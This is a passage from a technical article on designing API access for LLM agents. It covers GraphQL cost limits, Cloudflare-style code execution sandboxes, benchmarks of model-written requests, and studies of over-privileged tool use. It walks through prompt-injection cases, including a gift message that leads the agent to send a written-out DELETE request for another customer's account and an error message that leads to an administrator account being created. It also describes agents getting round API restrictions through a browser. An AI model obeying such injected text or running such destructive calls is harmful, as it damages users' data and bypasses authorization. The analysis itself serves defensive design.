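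A limit on nesting depth wouldn't help, because this query is only a few levels deep. *A Principled Approach to GraphQL Query Cost Analysis* (2020) generated random queries for the GitHub and Yelp APIs with at most ten levels of nesting and an estimated complexity of at most 1,000. The shop query would have stayed within the depth limit but exceeded the complexity limit tenfold. The Guild's *Demand Control*, the documentation for another GraphQL gateway, recommends using both kinds of limit.

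APIs score queries differently, so a limit is meaningful only together with its scoring rule. According to a reply in the Shopify developer forum thread *"query" field limits and calculated cost*, Shopify assigns zero points to plain values, one point to an object, and a number of points to each list that depends on the requested length. In *query complexity calculation*, Centra, another commerce platform, also assigns zero points to plain values, except for certain resource-intensive ones, which add two points each. Its example query for 100 orders with a few fields each scores 600 points. Saleor's *usage limits* shows a maximum of 50,000 points, but some of its fields add 100 points for every product in the list.

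The estimate needs a length for every list. If a field has no argument that limits the length, such as `first`, the developer has to supply an assumed size, which Apollo's gateway accepts through the `@listSize` directive. The estimate can also leave out some work. Shopify's, for example, is the same however complicated the search filter is.

An agent can also divide a refused query into smaller ones. A query for nine orders comes to 1 + 9 × 101 = 910 points, so the agent could fetch all 100 orders in 12 requests. To prevent this, the shop needs a total budget per customer or session as well as a limit per query.

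Cost limits don't replace permission checks, because a query for sensitive data can have a low score. The query for 50 reviewers' email addresses scores only 103 points, one each for the order, the item, the product, the 50 reviews and the 50 authors.

### How accurately do models write GraphQL?

Most published scores for model-written GraphQL queries come from IBM researchers and a single collection of questions. Kesarwani and colleagues built the collection in 2024, with 957 test questions on 14 data sources. They gave each model the schema and a question, ran the query the model wrote, and compared its result with that of a correct query.

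The best of the ten models, IBM's Granite-34B-Code, scored 34% without an example in its prompt and 50% with one. With the example, it scored 78% on questions that needed only one type, 42% on those that required moving from one type to another, and 20% on those that required two such moves. These models are now old, but a model that handles a request for an order's status well may still struggle with questions that require moving between types.

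Putting better examples in the prompt helps somewhat. *Schema and Natural Language Aware In-Context Learning for Improved GraphQL Query Generation* (Gupta, Kesarwani and colleagues, 2025) chose examples by the structure of the schema as well as the wording of the question. This improved some models' performance by up to 20% on certain kinds of query.

Shbita, Gentile and colleagues (2026), in *A Systematic Approach for Large Language Models Debugging*, used the 2024 collection to find out why Granite-3.1-8B, a small model, did badly. It scored about 20% at first, and better prompts raised this only to 27%. Training on the collection's roughly 10,000 labelled examples raised the score to about 50%, and training on those examples mixed with a million general and technical ones raised it to about 60%.

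The researchers also trained the model on the test questions, and it then scored 96%. They conclude that the model could learn GraphQL but had seen too little of it. The lower scores after ordinary training are better evidence for this than the 96%, which the model could have reached by memorizing answers.

The most useful result for judging validation comes from *Autonomous Multi-modal Agents for ITOps Observability* (Siddharth, Garai and colleagues, 2026), which tested the open model Llama-3.3-70B on 1,164 questions over 13 schemas. Without examples, 85.7% of the model's queries were valid under the schema, but only 58.4% exactly matched the reference query. Adding three examples improved validity but not the match rate.

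For about 27% of the questions, the model wrote a query that passed validation but differed from the expected one. Some of these were probably correct, since two different queries can return the same data. The researchers couldn't count how many because their version of the collection has no records to run queries against. The rest would have returned the wrong data, such as all of a customer's orders instead of only the late ones, without any error message.

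One small comparison suggests that GraphQL is easier for models to write than free-form REST URLs. *Adaptations of AI models for querying the LandMatrix database in natural language* (2024) had three open models write requests to the same database of land deals through both kinds of API. With prompting alone, 42% to 69% of the GraphQL queries were valid, compared with 0% to 2% of the REST requests. The valid REST requests tended to have more accurate filters, but this finding has a narrow basis because only one model wrote valid REST requests with any success, and only as part of an agent.

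None of these studies tested a leading commercial model. The GraphQL AI Working Group did so in 2025 and found that Claude Sonnet 4.5 wrote the best operations, with GPT-5 models close behind. It gave no scores and called the ranking preliminary because it didn't yet have a reliable way to grade the answers.

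## What if the model writes code against the whole API?

A model that writes code can combine many API requests in one step, including ones that use different endpoints or change data. Cloudflare, which sells network and security services for websites, offers its entire API to agents this way. The code runs in a sandbox with no direct access to the network, but it can still send the API any request that the host code and the token allow.

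### Why tool schemas crowd the context

In ordinary function calling, every tool definition takes up part of the context window, the limited amount of text a model can take in at once, even if the model never uses the tool. A shop with ten tools would hardly notice, but Cloudflare's API has over 2,500 endpoints. Cloudflare gives these figures for offering all of them through MCP:

| Design | Tools | Tokens |
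|---|---|---|
| One tool per endpoint, full schemas | 2,594 | about 1,170,000 |
| One tool per endpoint, required parameters only | 2,594 | about 244,000 |
| Code Mode | 2 | about 1,000 |

Full schemas come to about 450 tokens per tool. The total is more than the context window of the most advanced models, according to Carey, in *Code Mode*, Cloudflare's announcement of the design. Code Mode is Cloudflare's name for having the model write code instead of calling each tool separately. Its two tools are `search`, for finding operations in the OpenAPI document, and `execute`, for sending requests. Each takes a single string of JavaScript. (Cloudflare has since added a third tool that searches its developer documentation.)

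The figures count only the tool definitions, but the code the model writes and the results that come back also take up context. In a small test with ten tasks, Rai (2026), in *Beyond Plain MCP*, measured the total for a similar pair of tools at about 4,100 tokens per task when there were 42 operations to search and about 11,900 when there were 2,000.

Cloudflare's figures also don't measure whether the agent completes its tasks. Carey follows one request, to protect a website from a flood of malicious traffic, through four tool calls. The published code finds and reads the existing settings but doesn't change them.

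The comparison with 1,170,000 tokens is generous to Code Mode, since nobody could run that design. A developer with thousands of tools could instead let the agent search for tools and load only the matching definitions. Carey objects that someone has to maintain the search function and that each matching tool still uses tokens. But the results of Code Mode's `search` use tokens too.

Tool results can take up even more space than definitions. In Anthropic's *Code execution with MCP*, an agent copies a meeting transcript from Google Drive into a customer record in Salesforce. With separate tool calls, the transcript passes through the model twice, which could add 50,000 tokens for a two-hour meeting. A program can pass the text from one service to the other without the model reading it.

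### One task from search to answer

Suppose the shop offers its API through Code Mode, and customer 77 asks which of their orders are late. The model starts with a program for `search`:

```
async () => {
  const { paths } = await codemode.spec();
  const found = {};
  for (const path in paths)
    if (path.includes("orders")) found[path] = Object.keys(paths[path]);
  return found;
}
```

This program sends no requests to the shop. It looks through the OpenAPI document inside the sandbox and returns the matching paths and methods:

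```
{ "/v1/orders": ["get"],
  "/v1/orders/{order_id}": ["get"],
  "/v1/orders/{order_id}/refunds": ["post"] }
```

The model now knows enough to write a program for `execute`:

```
async () => {
  const list = await codemode.request({
    method: "GET", path: "/v1/orders", query: { customer: 77 }
  });
  const late = [];
  for (const { id } of list.items) {
    const order = await codemode.request({ method: "GET", path: `/v1/orders/${id}` });
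    if (order.status !== "delivered" && new Date(order.due) < new Date())
      late.push({ id, carrier: order.carrier });
  }
  return late;
}
```

If the customer has twelve orders, this one tool call sends thirteen requests. The model then receives a short list of late orders instead of twelve complete replies. The gift messages stay in the sandbox, so a prompt injection in one of them never reaches the model. But that protection depends on what the model's program returns. A program ending in `return order` would have put the gift message into the context.

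The `codemode.request` function is part of the host code. Cloudflare's *Build a Code Mode MCP server* includes an example that looks roughly like this when adapted to the shop:

```
async function request({ method, path, query = {}, body }) {
  if (!path.startsWith("/")) throw new Error("invalid path");
  const url = new URL("https://api.shop.example" + path);
  for (const name in query) url.searchParams.set(name, query[name]);
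  const reply = await fetch(url, {
    method, body: JSON.stringify(body),
    headers: { Authorization: "Bearer " + token }
  });
  return reply.json();
}
```

The function fixes the host and adds the token, but passes on whatever method, path and body the program supplies. It gives the model more freedom than `shop_get(path)` because the program can also change data and call the function in a loop. The model even writes the customer number, which `get_order` took from the login session.

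### What the sandbox blocks

Cloudflare runs each program in an isolate, a separate compartment within V8, the JavaScript engine that Chrome uses. According to Carey, the isolate has no file system and no environment variables, the named settings where programs often keep credentials. By default, it also can't fetch external URLs, so code that tries to send a delivery address straight to attacker.example will fail. The shop's token stays in the host code, so a program that searches for it won't find it.

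Data can still leave through the shop's own API. If the API has an endpoint that can email anyone, the program can use it to send someone the delivery address. The program can also read everything in the OpenAPI document and the API's replies, so Cloudflare warns developers to keep secrets out of both.

Cloudflare cuts off results at about 6,000 tokens, but this protects only the model's context. If a program refunds a thousand orders and returns a long report, the host code shortens the report only after the refunds have gone through.

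A sandbox can also have flaws. Lutra Security's *@enclave-vm/core is vulnerable to Sandbox Escape* (2026) describes a flaw that let code escape from Enclave, a JavaScript sandbox made for agents, before version 2.11.1. The flaw has the maximum severity score of 10. CERT/CC, which coordinates reports of software vulnerabilities, describes a 2026 flaw in another sandbox, Terrarium, that gave code full control of the container around it. Escaped code can use any credential it can reach, so keeping the token on a different machine is safer.

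### An injected deletion on the permitted host

Cloudflare warns that "code execution does not replace authorization", and its documentation leaves much of the access control to the developer. The host code keeps the token, and users limit its permissions when they connect. On Cloudflare's own server, they do this by logging in through OAuth and selecting what the agent may do. Developers who want individual requests to be approved have to add that step themselves, and Cloudflare tells them to enforce it in the request function before anything changes.

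A developer who copies the example server keeps the token outside the sandbox but doesn't narrow its permissions, because the example forwards whatever token the caller presents, with all its access.

Suppose the customer now asks for the details of order 1042. The model's program returns the whole order, including a gift message that tells the agent to remove customer 12 as part of a routine clean-up. If the model follows the instruction, its next program contains this line:

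```
await codemode.request({ method: "DELETE", path: "/v1/customers/12" });
```

The program doesn't escape from the sandbox, contact another server or see the token. Whether it succeeds depends on the other checks:

| Check | Result |
|---|---|
| Sandbox | allows the call, because the program uses the request function |
| Path check in the request function | allows it, because the path starts with a slash |
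| Shared token with full access | allows it |
| Token that can only read orders | refuses it |
| Object-level authorization | refuses it, because customer 77 doesn't own account 12 |

If the message named customer 77 instead, even object-level authorization might allow the deletion, because customers can usually close their own accounts. Stopping it would require a token that doesn't permit account deletion, a rule in the request function, or asking the customer to confirm the deletion. A general prompt to approve each tool call wouldn't help much, because the customer would see only that the agent wants to run `execute`, and the deletion would be somewhere inside a JavaScript program.

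Restricting the request function to GET requests would stop this deletion, but the HTTP method doesn't reliably show what a request does. *DADL* (Dunkel, 2026) describes a search that uses POST but changes nothing, and a GET request to an administrative address that resets a cache. Dunkel's format for describing APIs, also called DADL, allows each operation to be labelled as read, write, admin or dangerous. The software that runs the operations still has to enforce the labels.

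### Code that calls predefined tools

A program doesn't need a general request function. The developer can instead provide one function for each permitted operation:

```
async () => {
  const waiting = [];
  for (const order_id of ["1042", "1057", "1063"]) {
    const order = await codemode.get_order({ order_id });
    if (order.status !== "delivered") waiting.push(order_id);
  }
  return waiting;
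}
```

The model decides which orders to look up and in what sequence, but every call still goes through the same `get_order` tool, with the same digits-only pattern and ownership check. Injected text can't make the program delete a customer if there is no function for that. Cloudflare supports this design with a single tool called `code`, which wraps an existing MCP server. Cloudflare recommends the wrapper for servers with a manageable number of tools, because the description of `code` includes every function's definition.

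In Anthropic's *Programmatic tool calling*, Claude writes a Python program that runs in a sandboxed container. When the program calls a tool, it pauses while the developer's host code handles the call as in ordinary function calling. The reply then goes to the program, and Claude reads only the program's final output.

Some of the usual controls are weaker here. Anthropic doesn't support strict schemas for tools that code can call, so validation in the host code matters more. The `allowed_callers` setting specifies whether Claude should call a tool directly or from code, but Anthropic describes it as guidance for the model. To enforce this, developers can have the host code check the `caller` field, which identifies where each call came from.

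The pause also gives a person about four minutes to approve a refund. After that, the program stops waiting, and Claude typically tries again. If the host code issues the refund just after the deadline, the second attempt could issue it again unless the host code recognises the repeat.

Predefined tools can save as much context as a general request function, without letting the model choose any method and path. In its post on code execution with MCP, Anthropic presents each tool as a file in a folder, and the agent opens only the files it needs. This reduces the transcript example from 150,000 tokens to 2,000. Dunkel combines predefined tools with `search` and `execute`, and reports that this cut the space for the definitions of 1,833 tools from about 142,000 tokens to about 1,000. Both figures come from the designs' own developers and, like Cloudflare's, don't measure task success.

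The remaining risk comes from combining calls that are each valid on their own. If the shop offers both `get_order` and a tool for posting product reviews, a program can read a delivery address with the first and publish it with the second.

### What injected text did in two tests

In *From Tool Orchestration to Code Execution*, Felendler, Gandhi and colleagues (2026) tested whether attacks could succeed without escaping the sandbox. They built an MCP server for a database that recorded who could open which doors. The server's tools could run queries, add users and grant access. The agents used GPT-4o or GPT-4.1 and called the tools from code.

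In one attack, a tool returned an error message containing an instruction to create an administrator account with full access. The agent's software passed the message to the model so the model could correct its program. The new program created the account and granted it access, then ran the query the user had asked for. Every action used a tool the program was allowed to call, so the sandbox did not block any of them.

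The researchers consider this attack exclusive to code execution, which is doubtful. In ordinary function calling, the host code also returns error messages to the model, and the model could respond by calling the tool that adds users. The paper reports that success rates were consistent across the two models but doesn't give the rates.

Rai compared the two designs using the open model Qwen3.8-27B. Attacks using text injected into tool results succeeded in about 16 of 108 runs with separate tool calls and 10 of 108 with code, a difference that could be chance. They never succeeded when another model first narrowed the list to the two or three tools that seemed relevant, mostly because the tools the attacker wanted were no longer available. Rai wrote the attacks himself and used only six tasks, so this is weak evidence about how common such attacks would be. But it gives a reason to doubt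 that code execution is much easier to attack than separate calls when the tools are the same.

Felendler and colleagues propose having a separate model inspect tool descriptions before the agent writes code, and inspect results and errors before the agent reads them. Together with a sandbox and checks on the code, this inspection stopped all the attacks they demonstrated. They didn't test these defences against attackers who knew about them.

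### Does writing code improve the results?

In most tests, agents that call predefined tools from code do at least as well as agents that call them one at a time. *The Bitter Lesson of Tool Calling* (Patel, Sen and colleagues, 2026) compared the two methods on 309 questions from BFCL v4, a standard test of function calling. Of 14 models from Anthropic and OpenAI, 11 did as well or better with code. The other three, GPT-4o, GPT-4.1 and GPT-5.4-mini, scored 20 to 27 percentage points lower with code. They often wrote the two characters `\n` where the program needed an actual line break, so the program failed to run.

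The researchers attribute this to older model generations, but GPT-5.4-mini came out months after GPT-5, which didn't have the problem. Developers should therefore test each model instead of relying on its age.

Code had a clearer advantage when a task needed many independent calls. With separate tool calls, Claude Sonnet 5 began to leave some out when a task needed more than about 70, but with code it still made all 100 in the largest test. The tools in this study only recorded the values they received and never returned real data, so the test shows that models can write the right calls but doesn't show whether their programs handle the replies correctly.

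Rai tested three open models on 119 tasks in a simulated company. The tools returned data, and Rai checked whether each task had produced the right outcome.

| Model | Separate calls | Code | Code, replies not described |
|---|---|---|---|
| Qwen3.8-27B | 85.7% | 99.2% | 97.5% |
| Gemma-4-26B-A4B | 86.6% | 89.1% | 66.4% |
| Nemotron-3-Nano | 36.1% | 55.5% | 16.0% |

Code also used 70% to 90% fewer tokens. Gemma's small gain in success could be due to chance. When the models had no description of what each tool returned (last column), two of the three did much worse with code than with separate calls. A model that calls `get_order` directly can read the reply before deciding what to do next, but a model writing a program has to name the right field in advance. MCP servers can leave out these descriptions, so a developer who wraps an existing server in code should add any that are missing.

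Writing the whole program in advance also makes it harder for the model to adapt to the results of its calls. Felendler and colleagues found that code and separate calls gave similar task quality on most of the ten MCP servers they tested, and that code used fewer tokens. On some tasks that involved three servers, code did worse because the program lacked a branch for a case that came up. An agent making separate calls could sometimes recover by reading the result and trying something else.

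None of these three studies gave the model a general request function like Cloudflare's, so they don't show how well models write methods and paths for a large API. *Is Bash All You Need?* (2026) tested agents with a command line, which gave them even more freedom. These agents did better and cost less than agents whose code could call only predefined tools. The paper still suggests predefined tools for companies whose security rules restrict agents to an approved list of actions.

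Writing code may not be worthwhile for the shop's simplest questions. In Anthropic's own tests, calling tools from code reduced billed input tokens by about 38% on a project-management benchmark with 75 tools, with no loss of accuracy. On τ²-bench, a set of customer-service tasks for airlines, shops and telephone companies, it cost about 8% more and left scores unchanged. Each turn in τ²-bench needed only one or two calls, and so does a customer's question about where order 1042 is.

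## How often does a model write the wrong request with no attacker present?

In the main benchmark of model-written web requests, the best model got 60% right when it wrote everything and 77% when it was given the address and method and wrote only the arguments. Limited access therefore prevents some errors, but the model can still supply a wrong value or make a valid call too early. After a failed call, many models also use a more powerful tool than the task needs.

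### Errors by part of the request

| Error | Example in the shop | Under limited access |
|---|---|---|
| Invented endpoint | `GET /v1/shipments/1042`, an address the shop doesn't have | impossible |
| Wrong endpoint | a customer's account instead of their order | possible only if a tool exists for it |
| Wrong method | `GET` instead of `POST` for a refund | impossible |
| Invented parameter | `?include=tracking` | host code can refuse it |
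| Missing parameter | a refund with no amount | host code can refuse it if the schema requires an amount |
| Wrong value | order 1024 instead of 1042 | possible |
| Wrong moment | a refund before the goods have come back | possible |

Many of the errors that a limited design prevents are the easiest to notice. An API returns "not found" for an invented address and usually rejects a request that lacks a required parameter, so nothing happens and the agent can try again. But if the model requests the wrong order, such as 1024, the API returns a normal reply about the wrong parcel. The worst structural errors produce valid requests, such as a DELETE request to a real address when the model should only have read the record.

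### How accurately models write whole requests

The benchmark by Maninger and colleagues has one task for each of the 395 endpoints of Asana (a project-management service), Google Calendar, Google Sheets and Slack. Gemini 1.5 Pro drafted the tasks from the APIs' specifications, and the researchers checked them all by hand. One task is to create a calendar with a particular name and time zone. The model being tested completes a line of JavaScript that sends the request, and the test software intercepts the request and compares it with the expected one.

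The researchers tested 21 open models, along with GPT-4o and GPT-4o mini. These are the results when the model wrote the method, the URL and the arguments:

| Measure | Open models | GPT-4o |
|---|---|---|
| Whole request correct | 0–30% | 60% |
| Correct URL | 32–72% | 78% |
| URL not in the API's specification | 14–39% | 9% |
| Correct method | mostly over 80% | 91% |
| Share of the model's arguments that were correct | 51–75% | 89% |
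| Share of the expected arguments that the model wrote | 33–69% | 87% |
| Correct value, if the argument's name was correct | 53–84% | 95% |

The first row covers all tasks, and the others cover only code that ran. Some open models scored zero because they couldn't continue the line of JavaScript at all, so we can learn little from those scores about their knowledge of APIs.

GPT-4o wrote the wrong URL 22% of the time. In 9% of all cases the URL didn't exist, so the API would have refused the request. In the other 13%, the URL was real but wrong for the task. Code Llama 70B, the best open model, also chose a real but wrong URL in 13% of cases. It made more URL errors than GPT-4o only because it invented more URLs.

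Supplying the correct method and URL raised GPT-4o's score from 60% to 77% and Code Llama's from 30% to 40%. The remaining errors were in the arguments. Among the open models, the endpoint doesn't accept 6% to 31% of the arguments they wrote.

These scores probably understate what an agent can do, because the models are old and had to recall each API from training, without the relevant documentation that a developer would normally supply. On the other hand, Slack and Google Calendar are popular services with many public code examples. No model can have memorised the shop's private API, so the scores may overstate how well an agent would use it.

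#### Restricting the output to the API's specification

*Mitigating Errors in LLM-Generated Web API Invocations* (Maninger, Chemnitz and colleagues, 2026) tests two remedies on 24 open models. One is constrained decoding, which providers use to enforce tool schemas. The researchers' software converts an OpenAPI document into rules that limit what the model can write next. Once the model has written GET, it can continue only with a URL that accepts GET. After the URL, it can name only that endpoint's parameters and give each one only a value of the right type. It can't close the list until it has included every required parameter.

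Illegal URLs, methods and arguments fell to zero for every model, as they should if the rules are correct. The share of correct requests rose too, but many were still wrong:

| Part the model wrote | Average correct, unrestricted | Average correct, restricted | Code Llama 70B, restricted |
|---|---|---|---|
| Whole request | 13% | 28% | 50% |
| Arguments only | 26% | 57% | 72% |

(The averages leave out models that never produced code that ran, so the 13% covers fewer models than the 28%.)

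Some of the remaining failures were programs that didn't run, which became more common under the restrictions. In the rest, the model wrote a request that the API would accept but that didn't do what the task asked. Some GraphQL queries likewise passed validation but fetched the wrong data.

This form of constrained decoding requires control over how the model selects each token, so the researchers couldn't apply it to the GPT models. Their unoptimised implementation also cut generation speed by about 70%, though others add almost no delay.

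#### Giving the model the documentation

The other remedy was to search the API's documentation for the task and put the five best-matching endpoints in the prompt. The right endpoint was among them 95% of the time. The models then invented far fewer endpoints, and the average score for whole requests rose from 13% to 22%. When the models already had the endpoint, the documentation barely changed the score, because they began adding parameters the task didn't need.

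A common example was Asana's `opt_pretty`, which formats replies for people to read. The models kept using it because every endpoint's documentation listed it. That parameter is harmless, but a model might just as easily add the shop's `expand=customer` and fetch personal data that nobody asked for. With `get_order`, the host code sets the fields, so the model can't change them.

The researchers also tested the models on 28 tasks from real programs on GitHub. Without help, the open models averaged 47% on whole requests, compared with 13% on the original tasks. They think the models did better because these programs use well-known APIs in common ways, which the models would have seen in training. With only 28 tasks, the 47% is a rough estimate.

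GPT-4o's score for writing only the arguments fell from 77% in the original study to 59% in this one, below GPT-4o mini's 63%. Maninger and colleagues call the differences between their studies small and attribute them to minor changes in the prompt and the software. A drop of 18 points isn't small, and if minor changes can cause it, none of these scores is a reliable estimate for another application. Both studies also tested only models from 2024 or earlier, so they don't measure how often current models make these errors.

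### Why a correct type doesn't ensure a correct value

In the original benchmark, GPT-4o wrote the wrong value for about 5% of the arguments it had named correctly. If these errors were independent, a request with four correctly named arguments would have all four values right about 81% of the time (0.95⁴ ≈ 0.81).

The tasks were also easier than an agent's work in one respect, because they stated the values. One asks the model to save the project with identifier '778899' as a template. An agent often has to find a value in an earlier reply. Suppose the shop's refund tool needs a payment number, and `get_order` returns this:

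```
{ "id": "1042", "customer": "77", "payment": "5310", "status": "delivered" }
```

All the values are strings. If the model puts "1042" in the `payment_id` parameter, the request passes the tool schema, and if payment 1042 exists, the shop may refund a different purchase. The parameter's type doesn't specify which field of which earlier reply the value must come from. A safer refund tool would take only the order number and let the host code look up the payment. The model would then copy one number instead of two, and the ownership check would cover that number.

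### Valid calls at the wrong moment

A call can have the right endpoint and values but come too early, before a required step. Ma, Li and colleagues (2026), in *The Detour Is the Danger*, tested this with twelve tasks that each required a protective step: backing up a file before changing it, scanning a document before uploading it, or validating access before querying a database. The agents received written instructions for these procedures, and the researchers judged the agents by what happened to the files and databases, not by what the agents reported.

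With every service working normally, the agents acted without the required protection in 84 of 251 runs (33.5%). Results differed greatly among the seven models, which included GPT-4.1, GPT-4o mini, Qwen Max and DeepSeek V4 Pro. In another part of the experiment, where the protective services had faults, GPT-4.1 mini went ahead without protection from the start in 25 of 36 runs, while DeepSeek Flash kept the protection in all 36.

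These agents called predefined tools, so limited access doesn't prevent this kind of error by itself. A tool schema describes one call and doesn't include what came before it. In the shop, the equivalent would be a refund issued before anyone has checked whether the goods came back. The refund tool can prevent this by checking for the return itself, so that the order of the model's calls no longer matters.

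### API agents compared with browsing agents

Wider access lets an agent complete tasks that a short list of tools doesn't cover. *Beyond Browsing* (Song, Xu and colleagues, 2024) compared three agents built on GPT-4o. One used websites by clicking and typing in a browser. Another read the API's documentation and wrote Python code to send requests. The third, a hybrid, could do either at each step.

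The tasks came from WebArena, a benchmark with working copies of several kinds of website. The table gives the percentage of tasks that each agent completed:

| Site | API endpoints | Browsing | API | Hybrid |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| GitLab | 988 | 12.8 | 43.9 | 44.4 |
| Map | 53 | 20.2 | 45.4 | 45.9 |
| Online shop | 556 | 10.2 | 25.1 | 25.7 |
| Shop administration | 556 | 22.0 | 20.3 | 41.2 |
| Discussion forum | 31 | 10.4 | 18.9 | 51.9 |
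| Tasks on several sites | – | 10.4 | 8.3 | 16.7 |
| All tasks | – | 14.8 | 29.2 | 38.9 |

The API agent did best where the API was well documented and covered most of what the site could do. In one GitLab task, the agents had to count one person's contributions to a project. The browsing agent scrolled through the list until it ran out of steps and answered zero. The API agent fetched the list and counted the entries with three lines of code.

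Researchers examined 100 of the API agent's attempts and found that 50 of the tasks were impossible through the API alone. Of the other 50, the agent completed 33, misunderstood six and made errors in the API calls on 11. Missing functions were a much bigger obstacle than badly written requests. Adding 13 endpoints to the forum's original 18 raised the agent's score there from 9.4% to 18.9%.

The hybrid agent solved 51.9% of the forum tasks. The browsing and API agents together would have solved only 29.3%, even if they had never solved the same task. Combining the two methods within a task may explain some of the gap. The hybrid also ran on the API agent's software instead of the browsing agent's, which may have made it better at browsing.

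The study gave all three agents extensive access and did not test one with a short list of predefined tools. Its results therefore support giving an agent access to more of a site's functions, but not necessarily letting the model write the requests. A developer might get much of the same benefit by adding the missing functions as narrow tools. The scores are also mainly of historical interest, because GPT-4o is now an old model. The results for command-line agents in *Is Bash All You Need?* are more recent evidence in favour of extensive access.

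One task also shows how an agent can use a browser to get around a restriction on the API. The task was to delete all negative reviews of a product, and the shop's API had no endpoint for that. The hybrid agent found the product through the API and then deleted the reviews by clicking through the administration pages. A developer who leaves a function out of the API tools to keep an agent from using it has to restrict the browser as well.

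### What agents do after a call fails

Suppose `get_order` returns an error because the shop's server is briefly overloaded. The agent could try again or tell the customer to come back later. If it also has a tool that exports the whole order database, it could use that instead and find order 1042 in the file.

Yang, Bu and colleagues (2026), in *When Lower Privileges Suffice*, built a benchmark of 544 such situations. Each offers three narrow tools and three broad ones, and any of the six can complete the task. In one scenario, the agent must change an employee's manager. The narrow tools go through the normal personnel process, while one of the broad tools writes directly to the database and skips validation. The first call to each narrow tool fails with a temporary error, and a second call to the same tool succeeds.

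The researchers counted how often an agent used a broad tool before it had tried all the narrow ones. Six of the eleven models did so in more than 30% of scenarios. The highest rate was 64.9%, for Qwen3-8B, a small open model. GPT-5.2's rate was 9.7%, and most of those cases followed repeated failures. It chose a broad tool first in 5 scenarios, after one failure in 13 scenarios, and after two failures in 35 scenarios.

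This way of counting misses an agent that tries each narrow tool once and then uses a broad one, even though a simple retry would have worked. Parkinson, Vallati and colleagues (2026), in *Does Showing Agents the Privilege of Their Tools Reduce Over-Privileged Tool Selection?*, repeated the test with eight models and counted those cases as well:

| Model | Broad tool before trying all narrow ones | Broad tool at any point | Task completed without a broad tool |
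|---|---|---|---|
| Qwen3-8B | 56.6% | 70.4% | 6.4% |
| Qwen3-30B-A3B | 63.4% | 87.7% | 11.8% |
| Llama-3.1-8B | 12.9% | 12.9% | 69.1% |
| DeepSeek-v3.2 | 18.6% | 62.9% | 3.9% |
| Kimi K2.5 | 18.0% | 87.3% | 5.5% |
| Qwen3.5-397B | 38.4% | 77.2% | 18.8% |
| GPT-5.2 | 5.7% | 16.0% | 50.9% |
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | 1.5% | 7.9% | 11.9% |

Kimi used a broad tool in 87% of scenarios, although it looks fairly cautious in the first column. Tool failures were the main cause. When every tool worked on the first try, Qwen3-8B used a broad tool in only 8% of scenarios and Qwen3-30B-A3B in 6%.

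Claude Sonnet 4.6 usually tried each narrow tool once, then stopped and reported the problem. It seldom used excessive authority, but it completed few tasks. Llama often responded to an error by calling a tool that didn't exist. Host code can refuse such calls. Yang and colleagues had measured a rate of 55.9% for the same Llama model, compared with 12.9% here. The results for small models therefore seem to depend heavily on the setup.

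Telling the model to use the least powerful tool and to retry before choosing a stronger one reduced GPT-5.2's use of broad tools from 16.0% to 4.8%, and Qwen3.5-397B's from 77.2% to 53.5%. Labeling each tool with how much authority it had lowered these figures further, to 2.4% and 39.3%. Training a model to refuse harmful requests didn't reliably help. When Yang and colleagues tested such training on two small models, one of them used broad tools more often afterward.

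The benchmark rewards retrying, which is safe when reading an order but can issue a refund twice. The tests also used simulated, predefined tools. An agent that writes its own URLs can always try a broader request, such as listing all orders, which an agent with only `get_order` can't do. Neither study measured how often models try broader requests.

#### When the failed call is a safety check

Ma and colleagues also made services fail during their twelve tasks. When the faults were random, agents dropped a required protection after a fault in 9 of 247 runs (3.6%). When the faults targeted the backup, scanning or validation service, agents did so in 41 of 249 runs (16.5%), partly because random faults hit those services less often. The researchers have in mind an attacker who deliberately overloads a service, but an ordinary outage would look the same to the agent. In 39 of these 50 runs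 the agent still completed the task, so a developer who checked only for completion would have missed the problem.

In a further experiment with four of the models, DeepSeek V4 Pro dropped the protection more often when the service could fail repeatedly. It did so in 7 of 36 runs when the service could fail once, 16 when it could fail twice and 20 when it could fail three times. Qwen Plus showed no such trend. Clearer error messages made little difference overall. The agents dropped the protection about equally often whether the service reported that the check had failed, was incomplete or had an unknown status. In 68 runs, an agent planned to continue even after a verification tool had correctly reported that the protection wasn't in place.

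Ma and colleagues observed 97 unprotected actions in runs where host code did not check the requirements before each action, and none in the 576 planned runs where it did. They point out that a correctly built check should give this result. However, some agents abandoned the task when the host code blocked an action. With the protective services failing, DeepSeek Flash completed 28 of 36 tasks when the host code only blocked unsafe actions. When the host code also explained what was missing and how to proceed safely, it completed the task in all 35 finished runs.

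## How should a designer choose and enforce the split?

A designer should decide separately for each operation how much of the request the model writes, because a bad request can do more harm in some operations than in others. The shop's agent can safely compose its own product searches, but for a refund it should supply little more than an order number. In both cases, code outside the model must check the request before it runs.

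### Five questions about each operation

One consideration is whether the operation writes data. A wrong read can mislead the customer or reveal private information, while a wrong write also changes the shop's records, stock or money.

The split should depend partly on whether the shop can undo a call. Staff can restore a cancelled newsletter subscription in seconds, but they may never recover a refund that went to a stranger's card. Reads can also be irreversible, because the shop can't take back information it has disclosed.

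The split should depend partly on whose data the operation can reach. If it can reach only the public catalogue, an attacker gains little by changing the request. Reach depends on the credential as well as the tool, because a tool meant for one customer's orders may run with a token that gives access to every customer's orders.

A designer should ask both whether the model has read untrusted text and whether the result can leave the system. OpenAI analyses attacks on ChatGPT in terms of a source, which lets the attacker influence the agent, and a sink, a capability that becomes dangerous in the wrong context. An attacker needs both. A gift message is a source, and an email, a payment or a request to another server can be a sink.

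The question about untrusted text is harder to answer for a single operation, because all operations share one conversation. If the model read a gift message while tracking an order, the message is still in its context when the customer asks for a refund. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues base their designs on the principle that once an agent has read untrusted input, that input must not be able to trigger any consequential action. Host code can apply this principle by recording what the model has read and, once that includes untrusted text, withdrawing the riskier tools for the rest of the conversation.

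### Five operations in the shop

| Operation | Writes? | Can the shop undo it? | Whose data? | Untrusted text? | Can the result leave? | What the model should write |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Track an order | no | not a disclosure | the customer's | only if the reply includes the gift message | to the customer | an order number |
| Search products | no | nothing to undo | public | yes, in reviews | yes, harmlessly | search words and filters, or a whole query |
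| Issue a refund | yes | rarely | the customer's | possibly | yes, as money | an order number and a reason |
| Change a delivery address | yes | until the parcel ships | the customer's | possibly | yes, as a parcel | an order number and the new address |
| Run an ad hoc sales report | no | not a disclosure | every customer's, unless the shop removes personal data | possibly, in free-text fields | to one employee | a whole query on a read-only copy |

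The two operations with extensive access need different safeguards. Product search is safe because the data is public, provided the search tool can't reach anything else. The sales report is safe only if the shop takes several precautions, such as removing names, addresses and gift messages from the copy of the database. The report also belongs in a separate agent for employees, so that no customer's conversation can reach it.

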